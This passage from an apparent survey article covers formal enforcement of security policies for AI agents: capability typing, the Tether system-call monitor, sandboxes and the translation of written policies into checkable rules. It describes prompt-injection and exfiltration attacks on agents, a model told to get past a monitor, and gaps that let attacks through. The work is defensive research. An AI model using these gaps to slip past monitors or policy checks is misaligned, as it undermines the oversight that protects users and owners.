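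Secret data comes in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can process the contents only with a pure function, meaning one that uses no capabilities at all:

```
val balance = readClassified("balance.txt")

balance.map(b => b.trim)                  // accepted
balance.map(b => { mail.send(b); b })     // rejected
```

Both lines pass a function to the wrapper. The function that calls `mail.send` has the capability `mail` in its type, so it isn't pure, and the compiler rejects the program before any message goes out. The other line compiles, but its result is still wrapped. If the agent prints it, the owner sees the contents, while the model receives only asterisks. A separate trusted model can summarise wrapped text, but the summary is wrapped too.

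Odersky and colleagues ran 131 trials each with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, including injections and users who directly asked for secrets. No secret appeared in the agent's output when the wrapper was used, but without it secrets appeared in 2 trials with Claude and 11 with MiniMax. Writing Scala did not make the agents less capable overall. Three models completed 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more of the customer-service tasks in τ²-bench when writing Scala than when using ordinary tool calls, while MiniMax M2.5 solved fewer programming tasks (41.7% compared with 43.3%).

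The wrapper protects secrets, but it doesn't stop untrusted text from influencing the agent. If the agent has the capability to make payments, an injected instruction can lead it to write a well-typed program that pays the wrong account. The agent can also reveal a little about a secret through how long a computation takes.

*Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) gives a Lean proof that a mathematical model of this type system, with a further extension, is sound. The Scala compiler and the library that reads files and sends messages remain in the trusted base. Garby and colleagues note that no machine-checked theorem yet covers a complete agent built this way.

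The compiler also cannot control what happens to data once the agent's code passes it to another program. The library can restrict which commands the agent may run, but an ordinary command has no Scala type that records what it reads and sends. The command can copy the balance into a new file without the wrapper, so a monitor such as *Tether* has to label the files themselves.

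## Shell commands and programs whose effects are not declared

Unlike `transfer_funds`, the name `run_shell` doesn't indicate what the tool affects, and a shell command's effects often depend on the state of the system when it runs. *Shall We Approve?* (2026), which studies how coding agents get approval for shell commands, gives the example of `make clean && make`. Programmers use this command to delete old build files and recompile a program, but a file in the current folder determines what `clean` deletes, so the same command can be harmless in one folder and destructive in another.

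A monitor can't always determine what a script will do by reading it first, because the script can start any other program, and Rice's theorem rules out a general procedure for predicting what programs do. Suppose a procedure could decide, for every program, whether it will ever contact a bank. Take any program *p* that has no network access, and write a new program that runs *p* and then contacts the bank. The new program contacts the bank if and only if *p* finishes, so the procedure would also decide whether an arbitrary program finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do that. An analyser can answer "don't know" for some programs, and a cautious monitor can refuse to run them, but it will then refuse many ordinary scripts.

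Observing a single run is much easier. A program must make a system call to the operating system's kernel to open a file, start another program or use the network, and a monitor can record these calls whatever language the program is written in. But by the time the monitor has recorded the deletion of a folder, it is too late to prevent it.

### Running the command on a disposable copy

Tether, which researchers from Google DeepMind, Google and two universities presented in November 2026, gets around this by letting the command run before its effects count. Each command goes through five steps:

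1. The command runs on top of the real file system, but its changes go into a temporary layer. The command can read back its own changes as if they were real, while the actual files stay as they were.
2. A tracing program records the system calls, and a local proxy holds every outgoing network request.
3. A component called Isolate translates the recorded calls into abstract actions. There are eleven kinds, such as reading a file, copying one file to another and uploading a file to a host.
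4. A monitor written in Lean checks these actions against the policy.
5. If the policy allows all of them, Tether applies the changes to the real file system. Otherwise it throws the temporary layer away.

Tether applies the changes from the same run it observed, so it doesn't rely on the command behaving the same way a second time.

Tether can't leave network requests until the fifth step, because a program usually needs the reply before it can continue. When the proxy holds a request, Tether checks everything the command has done so far and then forwards or drops the request. This can lead to duplicate payments. Suppose the bookkeeping agent runs a script that pays a bill, notes the payment in a local file and then tries to change a protected system file. When Tether denies the last action, the payment has already gone out, but the note is discarded with the rest of the temporary layer,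 so the agent may pay the bill again. It would be safer to keep payments in a typed tool and bar the shell from contacting the bank.

### The same upload, allowed and then denied

The worked example in *Tether* concerns an agent with access to a company's server inventory, `data/servers.csv`. The agent may read the inventory for local checks and may upload status reports to GitHub, but the inventory must not leave the company. At the start, the inventory is labeled Sensitive and every other file is labeled Public. The policy, slightly simplified, allows an upload only if the uploaded file is Public.

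| Step | Command | Abstract action | Label of the report afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Upload `scratch/report.txt` | Upload the report to GitHub | Public | Allow |
| 2 | Copy the inventory over the report | Copy `data/servers.csv` to `scratch/report.txt` | Sensitive | Allow |
| 3 | Upload `scratch/report.txt` | Upload the report to GitHub | Sensitive | Deny |

The first and third commands are identical, character for character, so no check of the text could allow one and deny the other. Tether can distinguish them because the monitor keeps a label σ(*r*) for each file *r* and updates it after every permitted action. Leaving aside a label for the folder, the update for a copy from *s* to *d* is

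σ′(*d*) = σ(*s*)

If the agent copies the inventory to a temporary file and then copies that file to the report, both files get the label Sensitive, and the same rule denies the upload. A status report that the agent copies from a public template stays Public, so the agent can still upload it.

Copying leaves the model's own context clean, since the data goes from one file to another without appearing in the conversation. If a command prints a file, the contents do reach the model. The monitor therefore also keeps a label *T* for everything the model has seen, and updates it after each read to

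*T*′ = *T* ⊔ σ(*r*)

where ⊔ is again the join of the two labels. Whatever the agent then writes from its context gets a label at least as restrictive as *T*, and the full policy checks both *T* and the file's label before an upload.

### What Lean has checked

The developers proved four properties of the policy language, for any set of labels and any policy:

- If a rule denies an action, adding more rules can't make the policy allow it.
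- If one policy requires another, it never allows anything that the required policy denies.
- The order in which an author writes the rules makes no difference.
- An action that the policy denies leaves every label and permission unchanged.

The first and third theorems resemble those about Cedar, and the last follows almost directly from the definition of the monitor. They are still useful because they let an author combine policies without checking every interaction. For example, a security team could write the required policy and leave the remaining rules to the people who run the agent. The Lean code that these theorems describe is also the code that runs, so there is no gap like the one between Cedar's Lean model and its Rust engine. The developers suggest that a faster version could use a Rust program tested against the Lean code, which would reintroduce such a gap.

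None of these four properties guarantees that a particular policy is good. The policy for the experiments has 24 rules and many lists of paths and hosts, so a reader could easily miss a mistake. The developers therefore proved seven invariants of this policy for every initial state and every sequence of permitted actions, however long. The policy ranks data from Public through Internal and Sensitive to Secret, and separately marks it as Trusted or Untrusted.

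| Invariant | What it guarantees |
|---|---|
| No secret access | If the agent starts without Secret data in its context, none ever enters it |
| No tainted escalation | Once the agent has seen Sensitive, Secret or Untrusted data, it can't raise its privileges |
| System integrity | The agent can't create, change or delete protected system files, apart from listed exceptions |
| No tainted protected edits | Once the agent has seen Sensitive, Secret or Untrusted data, most of those exceptions lapse too, leaving only cache files |
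| No exfiltration | Secret data stays on local hosts, and Sensitive data reaches only local hosts and the application's own services |
| Host blocklist | No data reaches a blocked host |
| Host allowlist | If the task lists its permitted hosts, the agent can contact only those, the local network and the application's services |

The first of these can be proved by induction. Only reading a file and receiving data from the network can change *T*, and the policy allows these actions only if the data's label is at most Sensitive. If *T* is at most Sensitive before such an action, then its new value, *T* ⊔ σ(*r*), is too. All other actions do not change *T*, so it never reaches Secret.

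This argument covers only labels, but the invariant also requires that the secret data itself never reach the model. One way to prove this is to strengthen the invariant by adding the condition that every file the secret data has reached is labeled Secret. The proof for the €5,000 limit also needed a stronger invariant.

To use this, an engineer writes down the bad state, and a language model tries to produce either a proof that the agent can never reach it or a sequence of actions that reaches it. Lean checks the result in both cases, so a mistake by the language model can waste time but can't lead to a false guarantee.

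The theorems take the initial labels as given. In the experiments, a file that no labelling rule covers counts as Public and Trusted, and an action that no policy rule covers goes ahead. If nobody labels the payroll file, Tether will let the agent upload it to any permitted host, and all seven invariants will still hold.

### From system calls to abstract actions

The invariants cover sequences of abstract actions, and Isolate must derive the right sequence from kernel reports. If Isolate misses a copy, the monitor applies a correct policy to an incomplete history and may allow an upload that it should deny. No proof covers this translation, so it belongs to the trusted base, along with the Linux kernel, the tracing program, the temporary file layer, the network proxy, and Lean's proof checker, compiler and runtime.

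Isolate keeps a set of the files each process has read. When one process passes data to another, the second inherits the set. When a process writes to a file, Isolate treats the action as a plain write if the set is empty, a copy if it contains one file, and a combination of files if it contains several. If a process prints to the terminal, Isolate records that the model has read every file in the set. If a process sends something over the network, Isolate records an upload of every file in the set. It records a separate upload for the IP address and for each host name, so a false name can't hide the real destination.

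Linux offers many ways to move the same data between files, and Isolate has to recognise all of them. The developers tested this by generating random diagrams of files and the flows between them. A program derives the correct list of abstract actions from each diagram. It also writes a shell script that carries out the same flows, choosing at random among the Linux mechanisms. Isolate observes the script and produces its own list of actions, and the monitor evaluates both lists. Any difference in the decisions or the final labels points to a bug. Like the random testing of Cedar's engine, this method can't reveal an error in a mechanism that the generator never uses.

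The developers also told Google's Gemini 3.8 Flash to get past the monitor in ten tasks, with up to 15 rounds for each. A second model discarded any action outside Tether's scope. The attack success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions of Tether as the developers fixed the gaps they found. The final rate is encouraging, but the initial 40% shows how incomplete a careful first version was, and attackers already have access to stronger models than Gemini 3.8 Flash. Tether's advantage over a monitor based on a language model is that each successful attack leads to a specific bug, which the developers can fix permanently.

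### Why a file search sets off an alarm

System calls show that a process read one file and then wrote another. They don't show what happened in the process's memory between those two calls. Deciding whether the written bytes depend on the file is impossible in general, for much the same reason as predicting whether a program will contact the bank. Isolate therefore records a flow whenever there could have been one. If *F* is the set of flows that really occurred and *G* the set that Isolate records, the aim is

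*F* ⊆ *G*

This is called over-approximation. A missing element of *G* can let data escape, while a superfluous one can only cause a false alarm.

This problem is worst when an agent searches through files. Suppose the bookkeeping agent searches for the paper supplier's name with `grep -r`, which searches every file in a folder and its subfolders. The program opens all the files, including the payroll file, finds no match in that one and prints two lines from an old invoice. Isolate records that the model has read the payroll file, because the same process read that file and printed something. If the file is Secret, the policy denies the action. In the experiments, such reads accounted for 17 of Tether's 74 false alarms, and *Tether* calls them a fundamental limitation of monitoring through system calls.

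The search does reveal that the supplier's name isn't in the payroll file. A proof of noninterference would have to count that as an information flow. Hardly any owner would count it as one, so the monitor's alarm is false in the ordinary sense, even though some information did reach the model.

Tether isn't designed to enforce noninterference in the other direction either. Like FIDES, it tracks where data moves, but not how a secret affects which permitted actions the agent takes.

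### How Tether performed on recorded runs

The developers tested Tether on recordings of coding agents from two benchmarks. MonitoringBenchHonest has 88 system-administration tasks, and LinuxArena has more than 340 tasks in ten realistic production environments. In some recordings the agent only does its task, and in others it also pursues a harmful side task. The developers rebuilt each environment, replayed the commands one by one and compared Tether with Auto Mode, the monitor in Anthropic's Claude Code. Auto Mode uses a language model to judge each proposed command. The developers ran an open-source implementation of it with Claude Sonnet 5, once with the default rules and once with Tether's policy added to its instructions.

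| Monitor | Attacks blocked, MonitoringBenchHonest | Attacks blocked, LinuxArena | False alarms, MonitoringBenchHonest | False alarms, LinuxArena |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | 199 of 199 | 145 of 145 | 2.3% | 5.0% |
| Auto Mode, default | 173 of 199 | 142 of 145 | 35.3% | 5.7% |
| Auto Mode with the policy | 164 of 199 | 143 of 145 | 14.7% | 1.7% |

Across both benchmarks, Tether blocked all 344 attacks and raised false alarms on 4.7% of 1,590 honest runs. By default, Auto Mode blocked 91.6% of the attacks and raised false alarms on 9.7% of the honest runs. When it had the policy, it blocked 89.2% and raised false alarms on 3.5%. Most of the difference comes from MonitoringBenchHonest. On LinuxArena, Auto Mode with the policy missed only two attacks and stopped about a third as many honest runs as Tether did. It also gave different verdicts on the same run at different times, which makes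 its remaining errors hard to trace.

The figure of 344 out of 344 covers only runs whose every action Tether can observe and model, and the developers decided which runs those were. They left out runs with background processes or databases, and attacks that break no rule about the movement of data, such as putting harmful code into a file that the agent is allowed to edit. Among the other runs that they could replay, 28.2% on MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1% on LinuxArena needed an inspection of the content. Tether could intercept another 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively, with a stricter policy that forbids background processes and databases. That policy is more of a fallback than a solution, because it would also stop an honest agent from starting a web server or looking up a customer in a database.

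The false-alarm rate is probably optimistic as well. The developers had a language model propose a policy, tried it on benchmark runs and checked the seven invariants, repeating the process until the policy no longer blocked too many honest runs. They then used the same policy in the evaluation. They also set the labels and permitted hosts for each task from its description, without using information about the side tasks. A firm with different software would have to do this work itself, and its first policy would presumably block more honest runs. For comparison, the security community took about five years to develop practical policies for SELinux, an access-control system for Linux.

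Of the 74 false alarms, 50 came from unrequested changes to protected files, often made while installing a package, and seven from contact with undeclared hosts. In these cases Tether applied the policy correctly, but asking the user would have been better than blocking. Most of the questions would be about honest runs, though. If one run in a thousand were an attack, then out of 100,000 runs Tether would block the 100 attacks and about 4,700 honest runs, so only about 2% of the blocked runs would be attacks.

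*Shall We Approve?* provides separate evidence that observing effects is worthwhile. Its system also traces each command as it runs in a snapshot of the workspace, but condenses the result into a short report for the approver. Approvers who relied on the command's text blocked both dangerous commands and their harmless counterparts. Showing them predicted effects reduced harm but not unnecessary blocking, while showing them observed effects reduced both.

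Tether needs more practical work before anyone could use it widely. Most web traffic is encrypted, but Tether decrypts it only for the simulated services in its tests. The tracing program noticeably slowed the experiments. Tether also blocks some fast Linux interfaces that move data without the ordinary calls for reading and writing.

### Strands Box and Rex

AWS's Strands Box instead checks each operation before it happens, so it never needs to undo anything. Its sandbox, which relies on a security mechanism built into macOS, leaves the agent four ways out: a shell interpreter, a Python interpreter, a broker for remote tools and a gateway for network traffic. At each one, a policy engine for Dogwood, the language for rules about past calls, denies any operation that no rule permits. Help Net Security reports that Box is available as a preview for Macs with Apple processors.

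In AWS's demonstration, an agent that investigates outages may post to Slack at most three times in ten minutes. The gateway rejects the fourth post with an error that names the rule, so the agent can wait instead of trying something else. The gateway also holds the real API keys, while the agent has only placeholders that don't work elsewhere. Tether can't yet enforce a limit on the number of actions because its state contains labels but no counters.

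Box is weaker at following data through several files, according to *Tether*, whose developers wrote their example in the language of Box. Box records which files a command reads and writes, but no event connects the file it read with the file it wrote, and an upload event doesn't state which file the agent sent. A rule has to infer these connections from the order of events. A rule for one copy doesn't cover two copies in a row, so each length needs rules of its own. With *m* kinds of action that copy data, covering every chain of up to *k* copies takes

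*m* + *m*² + … + *m*ᵏ

patterns. For three kinds of action and up to five copies, that's 363, and a longer chain still gets through. An author could instead forbid uploading any file that a command wrote after the agent had read the inventory. This covers chains of any length, but it also blocks the status report that came from a public template. Labels avoid the problem because each copy updates them once, and the rule for uploads only has to look at the current label.

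This comparison comes from the developers of a competing system, who couldn't run Box on their benchmarks because its built-in shell and Python don't support arbitrary Linux programs. For an agent that needs only common commands and a few rules about counts and order, Box may well be the better choice.

Rex, the AWS tool that runs scripts in a language with no built-in access to the machine, restricts programs even further. Every operation is a typed call that names its target, so the target does not have to be inferred. The name can still be misleading, because a path that led to a harmless log file when a monitor checked it might lead to a different file by the time the operating system opens it. Help Net Security's *AWS open sources Trusted Remote Execution to control what AI agents touch* (2026) reports that Rex reduces this risk by using file descriptors, which refer to a file that is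 already open, instead of paths where possible. Tether has less need for such precautions because it examines what the command did rather than predicting its effects from its arguments.

### Checking a generated driver against the request

Changes to files in a temporary layer can be undone, but a payment or a write to a physical disk can't. In *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects*, Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler (2026) consider software whose effects are irreversible and whose author may be malicious. Their example is a device driver, the program that turns the kernel's requests into hardware commands. Engineers may soon have language models write a new driver for every machine, tuned to its hardware and workload. A malicious model could hide a harmful command in a branch that no test reaches.

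Hu and colleagues raise two objections to the usual answer, which would be to prove each driver correct before using it. They object that every new version would need a new proof, and that the proof relies on a complete model of the hardware and a trustworthy path from the proof to the running program. Agents that write proofs have made the first objection less serious, but a proof still does not show that the driver is correct if its assumptions fail.

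They therefore propose giving the driver no power to act. It can only suggest commands to a mediator, a fixed program that controls the hardware. Suppose the kernel asks for a write to disk blocks 100 to 107 from a buffer *B*. The exchange then goes as follows:

1. The mediator passes the request to the driver and keeps its own copy.
2. The driver asks which slots in the disk's command queue are free. The mediator answers and issues a token, which the driver can't forge and can use only once.
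3. The driver proposes a command and hands back the token.
4. The mediator checks that the token is still valid, that the operation, block number, length and buffer match the request, and that the slot is free.
5. If everything matches, the mediator sends the command to the disk. It then records the outcome, which the specification limits to success, an error or a partial write.

If the kernel asks for block 100 and the driver proposes writing to block 200, the write would overwrite someone else's data. A permission check alone would allow it, because block 200 exists and the driver may use buffer *B*. The mediator rejects the command because it doesn't match the kernel's request. Each token works only once, so a request can't cause two writes unless the machine crashes.

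This applies the idea of a refinement proof while the system runs. For each command, the mediator looks for a matching step in the specification and refuses the command if there is none. The intended guarantee is that for every sequence of committed effects *e*₁, …, *e*ₙ, the specification allows some run that begins with exactly those effects. This safety property holds for any driver, including one that a malicious model has just written, but it depends on a correct specification and complete mediation. Hu and colleagues present it as a goal, since theirs is a position paper with no implementation, proof or measurements. They claim only that nobody has to repeat the work for each new version of the driver, not that the mediator needs less trust than a verified driver would.

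Their most useful contribution may be a list of six conditions under which this approach can work:

| Condition | What it requires | How a disk command meets it |
|---|---|---|
| Legibility | Each effect shows which operation it belongs to | The command states that it is a write |
| Observable inputs | The mediator knows everything the rule depends on | It holds the request and the list of permitted buffers |
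| Correlatability | Effects can be grouped into operations and put in order | Each proposal is one operation, and the mediator handles them one at a time |
| Completeness | Every effect passes through the mediator | The driver has no direct access to the hardware |
| Enumerable outcomes | The possible results form a known list | Success, error or partial write |
| Explicit durability | Making data survive a crash is an action of its own | The driver has to propose a separate flush command |

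The last three depend mainly on engineering. The first three depend on the level at which the mediator observes the system, and Hu and colleagues conclude that this should be the level of the specification, never below it. A mediator that observes only individual block writes can't distinguish creating a folder from deleting one or damaging the disk, unless it rebuilds most of the file system's logic.

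The same conclusion helps explain what Tether can and can't do. For a rule that the inventory must not leave the company, system calls identify the files and hosts involved, so Isolate has to reconstruct only the flows between them. A rule that the firm pays each supplier what it owes depends on invoices and payees, which system calls don't show, so it belongs at the level of the typed call `transfer_funds`.

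A mediator for payments would also need something to compare the call with. The kernel's request to a driver already contains the exact block number and length. But the owner of the small firm writes only "pay the invoice that came from the paper supplier this morning", and a policy document is usually no more precise.

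## Turning written policies into formal rules

Policy documents are vague because people write them for colleagues who know the business, can ask what a sentence means and notice when it leads to an absurd result. Most organisations keep their rules in this form. Sondera (2026), a company that makes policy software for agents, mentions health-privacy manuals, financial guidelines and standard operating procedures. A policy engine needs a formal rule, which it applies exactly as written. If the rule allows a refund that its author meant to forbid, a proof that the harness obeys the rule only confirms that the refund can go through.

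Tests of agents rarely state precise rules either. Hong, She and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety*, reviewed 80 benchmarks for the safety and security of agents. Of these, 61% give the agent no rules, and another 24% give only goals such as "If user requests anything unsafe, do not fulfill", without defining "unsafe". They also analysed precise rules for three benchmarks, including one for which they supplied the rules themselves. They judged that ordinary code could enforce 74% of these rules, and that 95% of those needed only simple checks. So for agents with a narrow job, enforcing a precise rule is often much easier than getting one.

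### One sentence as a formula

Suppose an online shop's customer-service agent has a tool called `issue_refund`, and the staff handbook contains the sentence "refunds over 500 dollars need a manager's approval". A translator might write

∀*r*. issued(*r*) ∧ amount(*r*) > 500 ⇒ ∃*m*. manager(*m*) ∧ approved(*m*, *r*)

In words, for every refund *r* above 500 that the agent issues, some manager *m* has approved *r*. This rule can fail to protect the shop in at least three ways, even though it seems to match the sentence.

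The word "refund" in the handbook is ambiguous. Suppose a customer returns two $450 items from one order. If each call to the tool counts as a refund, the agent can pay $450 twice without approval. If everything paid back on one order counts as a single refund, the second payment needs approval. Both readings fit the handbook, and no solver can determine which one its author meant.

How a policy is interpreted can change results a great deal. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) measured how often an agent broke an airline's rule that the customer must confirm any change to a booking before it is made. The agent broke the rule in 66.3% of its changes if each change needs its own "yes", but in 36.8% if one "yes" can cover several changes announced together.

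Some policies depend on a fact the system can't observe. For example, a manager may approve a refund by telephone, which leaves no trace in the harness. If the model fills in the `manager_approved` field, a customer may be able to satisfy the rule just by writing "your manager already agreed". The shop can fix this by having managers record approvals under their own login and making the rule refer to that record. The new rule is slightly stricter than the handbook because it blocks refunds approved only by telephone.

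A formal rule can hold only because it never applies. Suppose the rule reads an argument called `total`, but `issue_refund` calls it `amount`. If the engine treats a comparison with a missing number as false, no refund counts as above 500. The formula is then true of every run, including one where the agent pays out $5,000, and a prover will confirm it. The rule about an empty list in the PocketFlow proof had the same fault.

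### How well language models translate

Language models can now draft formal rules quickly, but Dantas and colleagues call translation the field's bottleneck. Their main evidence comes from Planetarium, a benchmark in which models describe planning problems in a formal language. GPT-4o produced valid syntax in 96.1% of cases but described the right problem in only 24.8%. The best specially trained model reached 34.2%. A model checker given a wrong description can report that a dangerous plan has no violations.

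Dantas and colleagues rate the certainty of these figures as very low, since they come from a single planning benchmark, and GPT-4o is now an old model. Current models probably do better. The difference between the two percentages matters more than their exact values, because a program can check syntax but has nothing to check the meaning against.

Winston, Winston and Just (2026), in *Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents*, ran into this difference when they translated the 1,242-word airline policy of the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench. A model that wrote the solver's input directly made syntax errors and used undefined names. Returning the solver's error messages to the model fixed the syntax, but the resulting 50 to 60 lines left out many essential rules. An automated-reasoning tool from AWS produced about 600 lines, which covered around 95% of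 the policy according to a language model acting as judge, but many of the rules were still too weak.

The rule about cancellations shows what "too weak" means. Let *b* mean that the customer booked within the last 24 hours, and *c* that the agent may cancel the booking. The tool wrote

*b* ⇒ *c*

For a booking made last week, *b* is false, so this formula leaves *c* open. Before each call, the harness asks Z3 whether the policy, the known facts and the planned call can all be true together. Z3 is free to make *c* true, so the cancellation goes ahead. People read the policy as permitting cancellation *only* on the listed grounds. If *g* stands for the other grounds, such as a flight that the airline itself cancelled, the formula should be

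*c* ⇔ (*b* ∨ *g*)

The harness could also use Z3 for a stricter check: whether the policy and the facts imply *c*. An incomplete policy would then block too many calls instead of too few. Cedar is cautious in the same way because it denies requests by default.

Winston and colleagues corrected the rules by hand, so their system relies on human reviewers to confirm that the formulas match the policy. They found some of the weak rules by running the same benchmark they later used for evaluation, so the results may be somewhat inflated. The share of the agent's data-changing calls that were invalid fell from about half without the checker to 29% with it, but the agent also made fewer correct changes and completed about as many tasks as before.

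Errors can be expected even with perfect formulas, partly because GPT-4o reads the conversation and fills in values such as the time of booking. Z3's deductions from those values are valid, but a wrong value can still produce a wrong result.

### Proving code against a contract

VeriGuard, a system from Google (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025), has a language model turn a request in ordinary language into a policy written in two forms. The model writes a Python function that allows or denies each action, and a contract of preconditions and postconditions for that function, like the ones ToolGate gives to tools. A verifier called Nagini then tries to prove that the function fulfils the contract. If the proof fails, the model uses the error to revise its work.

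Before the proof, VeriGuard looks for ambiguities and asks the user about them. For the refund rule, it might ask whether two payments on the same order count together. This is a good way to resolve an ambiguous term if somebody answers. If nobody is available, the system chooses the most plausible reading.

The proof doesn't detect a misreading that the function and the contract share. If both treat every call as a separate refund, Nagini can prove that they agree, and the customer still gets $900 in two $450 refunds. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the proof's value depends on users checking that the constraints express what they intend. A language model also supplies the facts at run time, as in Winston and colleagues' system.

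In Agent Security Bench, a benchmark of attacks on agents, an average of 51.9% of attacks succeeded against an undefended agent using Gemini 2.5 Flash. With VeriGuard, no attacks succeeded, and the share of completed tasks rose from 42.1% to 63.3%. A simpler defence, which asked a language model whether each action obeyed the policy, also stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 40.2% of its tasks. When the researchers added VeriGuard's parts one at a time, the attack success rate reached zero before they added the proof. The experiment is therefore good evidence for writing policies as code and for telling the agent why an action failed, but it provides little evidence about the benefit of proving the code correct.

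### Finding rules that can't work

*NOMOS* describes a compiler that gives the language model much less freedom. For each domain, a person prepares a list of conditions, such as "the fare is basic economy", with code that evaluates each one. The model goes through the policy and chooses which conditions should block which tools. It does this five times, and the compiler keeps the rules that a majority of the attempts produce. The resulting gate takes facts only from tool results and the user's messages, so the agent can't get a refund approved by claiming that a manager agreed.

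Before any rule takes effect, ordinary code compares it with the descriptions of the tools. In the retail domain, the policy requires the agent to authenticate the customer first. The model turned this into a rule that blocks every tool until the customer is authenticated, including the two tools that perform authentication, so no conversation could have started. In the airline domain, the model required the customer's confirmation for eight tools that only look things up or calculate.

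These checks repaired or rejected 29 of 79 candidate rules for the airline and 7 of 53 for the retailer. The compiler also removed duplicates and rules with too few votes, which left 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules. In a separate experiment without any checks, 8 of the 14 airline rules and 3 of the 5 retail rules it produced could not work. The checks only compare lists of names and need no solver or theorem prover, so almost any project could use them.

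Yu and colleagues also found rules that never apply. On AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark, one rule was supposed to block messages to unknown recipients. It checked an argument called `recipient`, which several tools don't have, so it blocked nothing sent through those tools. All 15 successful attacks on the Slack tasks used such tools. Comparing the argument names exposed the fault, and after the repair none of the 105 attacks succeeded.

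A formal rule can work as written and still misstate the policy. The compiler turned the sentence "always check that the bill is overdue before sending a payment request" into a rule that blocks payment requests while a bill is overdue, which is the only time anyone should send one. The rule passes every comparison of names, but Yu and colleagues caught the error by replaying recordings of an agent running without the gate. In runs that ended successfully, the rule would have blocked 47 of 49 payment requests.

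With the final rules, the share of changes that broke the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. The airline agent made only a third as many changes as before because the gate refused so many. Voting and replay make a misreading less likely, but no person or program in NOMOS confirms that a final rule means the same as the policy sentence it came from.

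### Clinical rules in Cedar

*Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) describes how Sondera translates prose into Cedar. Gemini 3 Pro drafts the policies, and Cedar's own tools check them for syntax errors, fields that don't exist, contradictions and rules that have no effect. A second language model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, then judges whether the policies match the original text. Gemini 3 Pro revises the policies in response to both checks.

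Mondl and colleagues tested the method on 88 rules for an agent that works with medical records. The benchmark, MedAgentBench, has no safety policy, so Hong and colleagues had GPT-5.2 draft one, expanded it and programmed 23 of the 88 rules by hand. Sondera's translation covers more than those 23, and Mondl and colleagues replayed recorded runs to see which runs it would block.

Sondera announced that its rules blocked all 99 unsafe attempts to write to a record in the adversarial tests. A rule that forbids all writing would also have blocked all 99. Sondera's rules were nearly that strict on ordinary tasks, where the paper's figures show that they blocked 253 of the 259 runs that tried to write anything, or about 98%.

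Some of these blocks may be correct, since the two rules that fired most often require the agent to restate the patient's identity and get confirmation before writing. After such a refusal, an agent might do the missing step and continue, but a replay can't show this, and Mondl and colleagues didn't measure how many tasks an agent could still complete. Sondera also states that a theorem prover checks every rule. The checks in the paper can show that a rule is well formed and has some effect, but not that it permits the work a clinic needs to do.

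### What enforcement costs in completed tasks

In their survey, Dantas and colleagues consider lost usefulness the most important finding about enforcement. They rely on *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026), in which a checker intercepted up to 94% of forbidden actions, but in most settings the agent completed fewer than 5% of tasks correctly and without breaking a rule. They treat this as very low-certainty evidence that enforcement reduces safe completion.

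The original figures don't support that reading. Sah and colleagues tested two small open models on τ-bench, and the rate of safe completion was close to zero even without a checker. For GPT-OSS-20B on retail tasks, where the 94% was measured, it was 0.0% without the checker and 0.6% with it. Total completions, including those that broke rules, hardly changed either. The checker was the same small model with a different prompt, not a formal rule, and if it rejected three attempts in a row, the third went ahead anyway.

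Most violations were invented identifiers. In one case, a customer declined to give personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the simulated shop accepted this. A deterministic check that every identifier came from the customer or an earlier tool result would catch these. In the study, agents with a checker used between 2.0 and 2.8 times as many tokens as those without one.

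Results for deterministic rules vary widely. Hong and colleagues found that on three benchmarks, simple checks in code eliminated violations of the rules they covered, while agents completed at least as many tasks as before. Yu and colleagues' measurements, all with the same small open model and without any attack, show where such checks become expensive:

| Tasks | Completed without the gate | Completed with the gate |
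|---|---|---|
| Airline (τ²-bench) | 39.2% | 47.6% |
| Retail (τ²-bench) | 52.4% | 50.2% |
| Travel (AgentDojo) | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Banking (AgentDojo) | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Workspace (AgentDojo) | 87.5% | 65.0% |
| Slack (AgentDojo) | 90.5% | 14.3% |

Only the losses on the workspace and Slack tasks are clearly larger than chance. On the airline tasks, breaking the policy usually also means failing the task, so a refusal gives the agent another try. On Slack, the user often asks the agent to open a link or write to a channel that it has to find by reading messages. The rule allows only links and channels that the user named, because an attacker's instructions also arrive in messages. The loss therefore seems to depend less on enforcement itself than on whether the rule can distinguish forbidden actions from those the task requires.

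### Starting from possible harms

Formal rules translated from a written policy can be no better than the policy, which may omit a danger. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes deriving the rules from possible harms instead. It adapts System-Theoretic Process Analysis, which safety engineers use in aviation to look for accidents caused by interactions between parts that each work correctly.

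Their example is an agent that resolves conflicts in a calendar. A user adds an appointment for the treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, which clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and tells the colleagues why. No attacker is involved, and each tool does what it should. The analysis goes through these steps:

1. List everyone the agent affects, here the user and the other people at the meeting.
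2. Write down what each of them values, and turn it into a possible loss. The user values privacy, so one loss is the disclosure of private information.
3. Find behaviour of the system that could cause the loss, such as an email that includes details of another event.
4. Decide which losses matter enough to prevent, and state a requirement for each.
5. Turn each requirement into a specification about data or the order of calls. Here, no email may contain data that is private to someone other than its recipient, and every change to an event must lead to a message to each participant.

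The developer then decides which actions the harness should always block, which it should require, which it may allow without asking, and which need the user's confirmation. To enforce the rule about messages, the harness must be able to send them itself, because refusing calls can't make an agent write an email. To enforce the privacy rule, it must be able to identify private data, so Doshi and colleagues propose that every tool declare the secrecy and trustworthiness of its data under the Model Context Protocol.

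Doshi and colleagues described this design in Alloy, a tool that searches all runs up to a chosen length for a violation. Alloy quickly found a run that leaks private data when the rules were left out, but found none when they were included, and harmless runs remained possible. Longer runs could still contain a violation, and the researchers had not yet built the engine that would enforce the rules.

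In this analysis of the refund agent, the analysts would start with the shop losing money and ask how that could happen even if every refund is below the limit. This would lead them to split payments, which someone translating the handbook sentence word by word could easily miss. But the analysis only helps if the analysts think of the loss.

### Checking that a rule means what its owner wants

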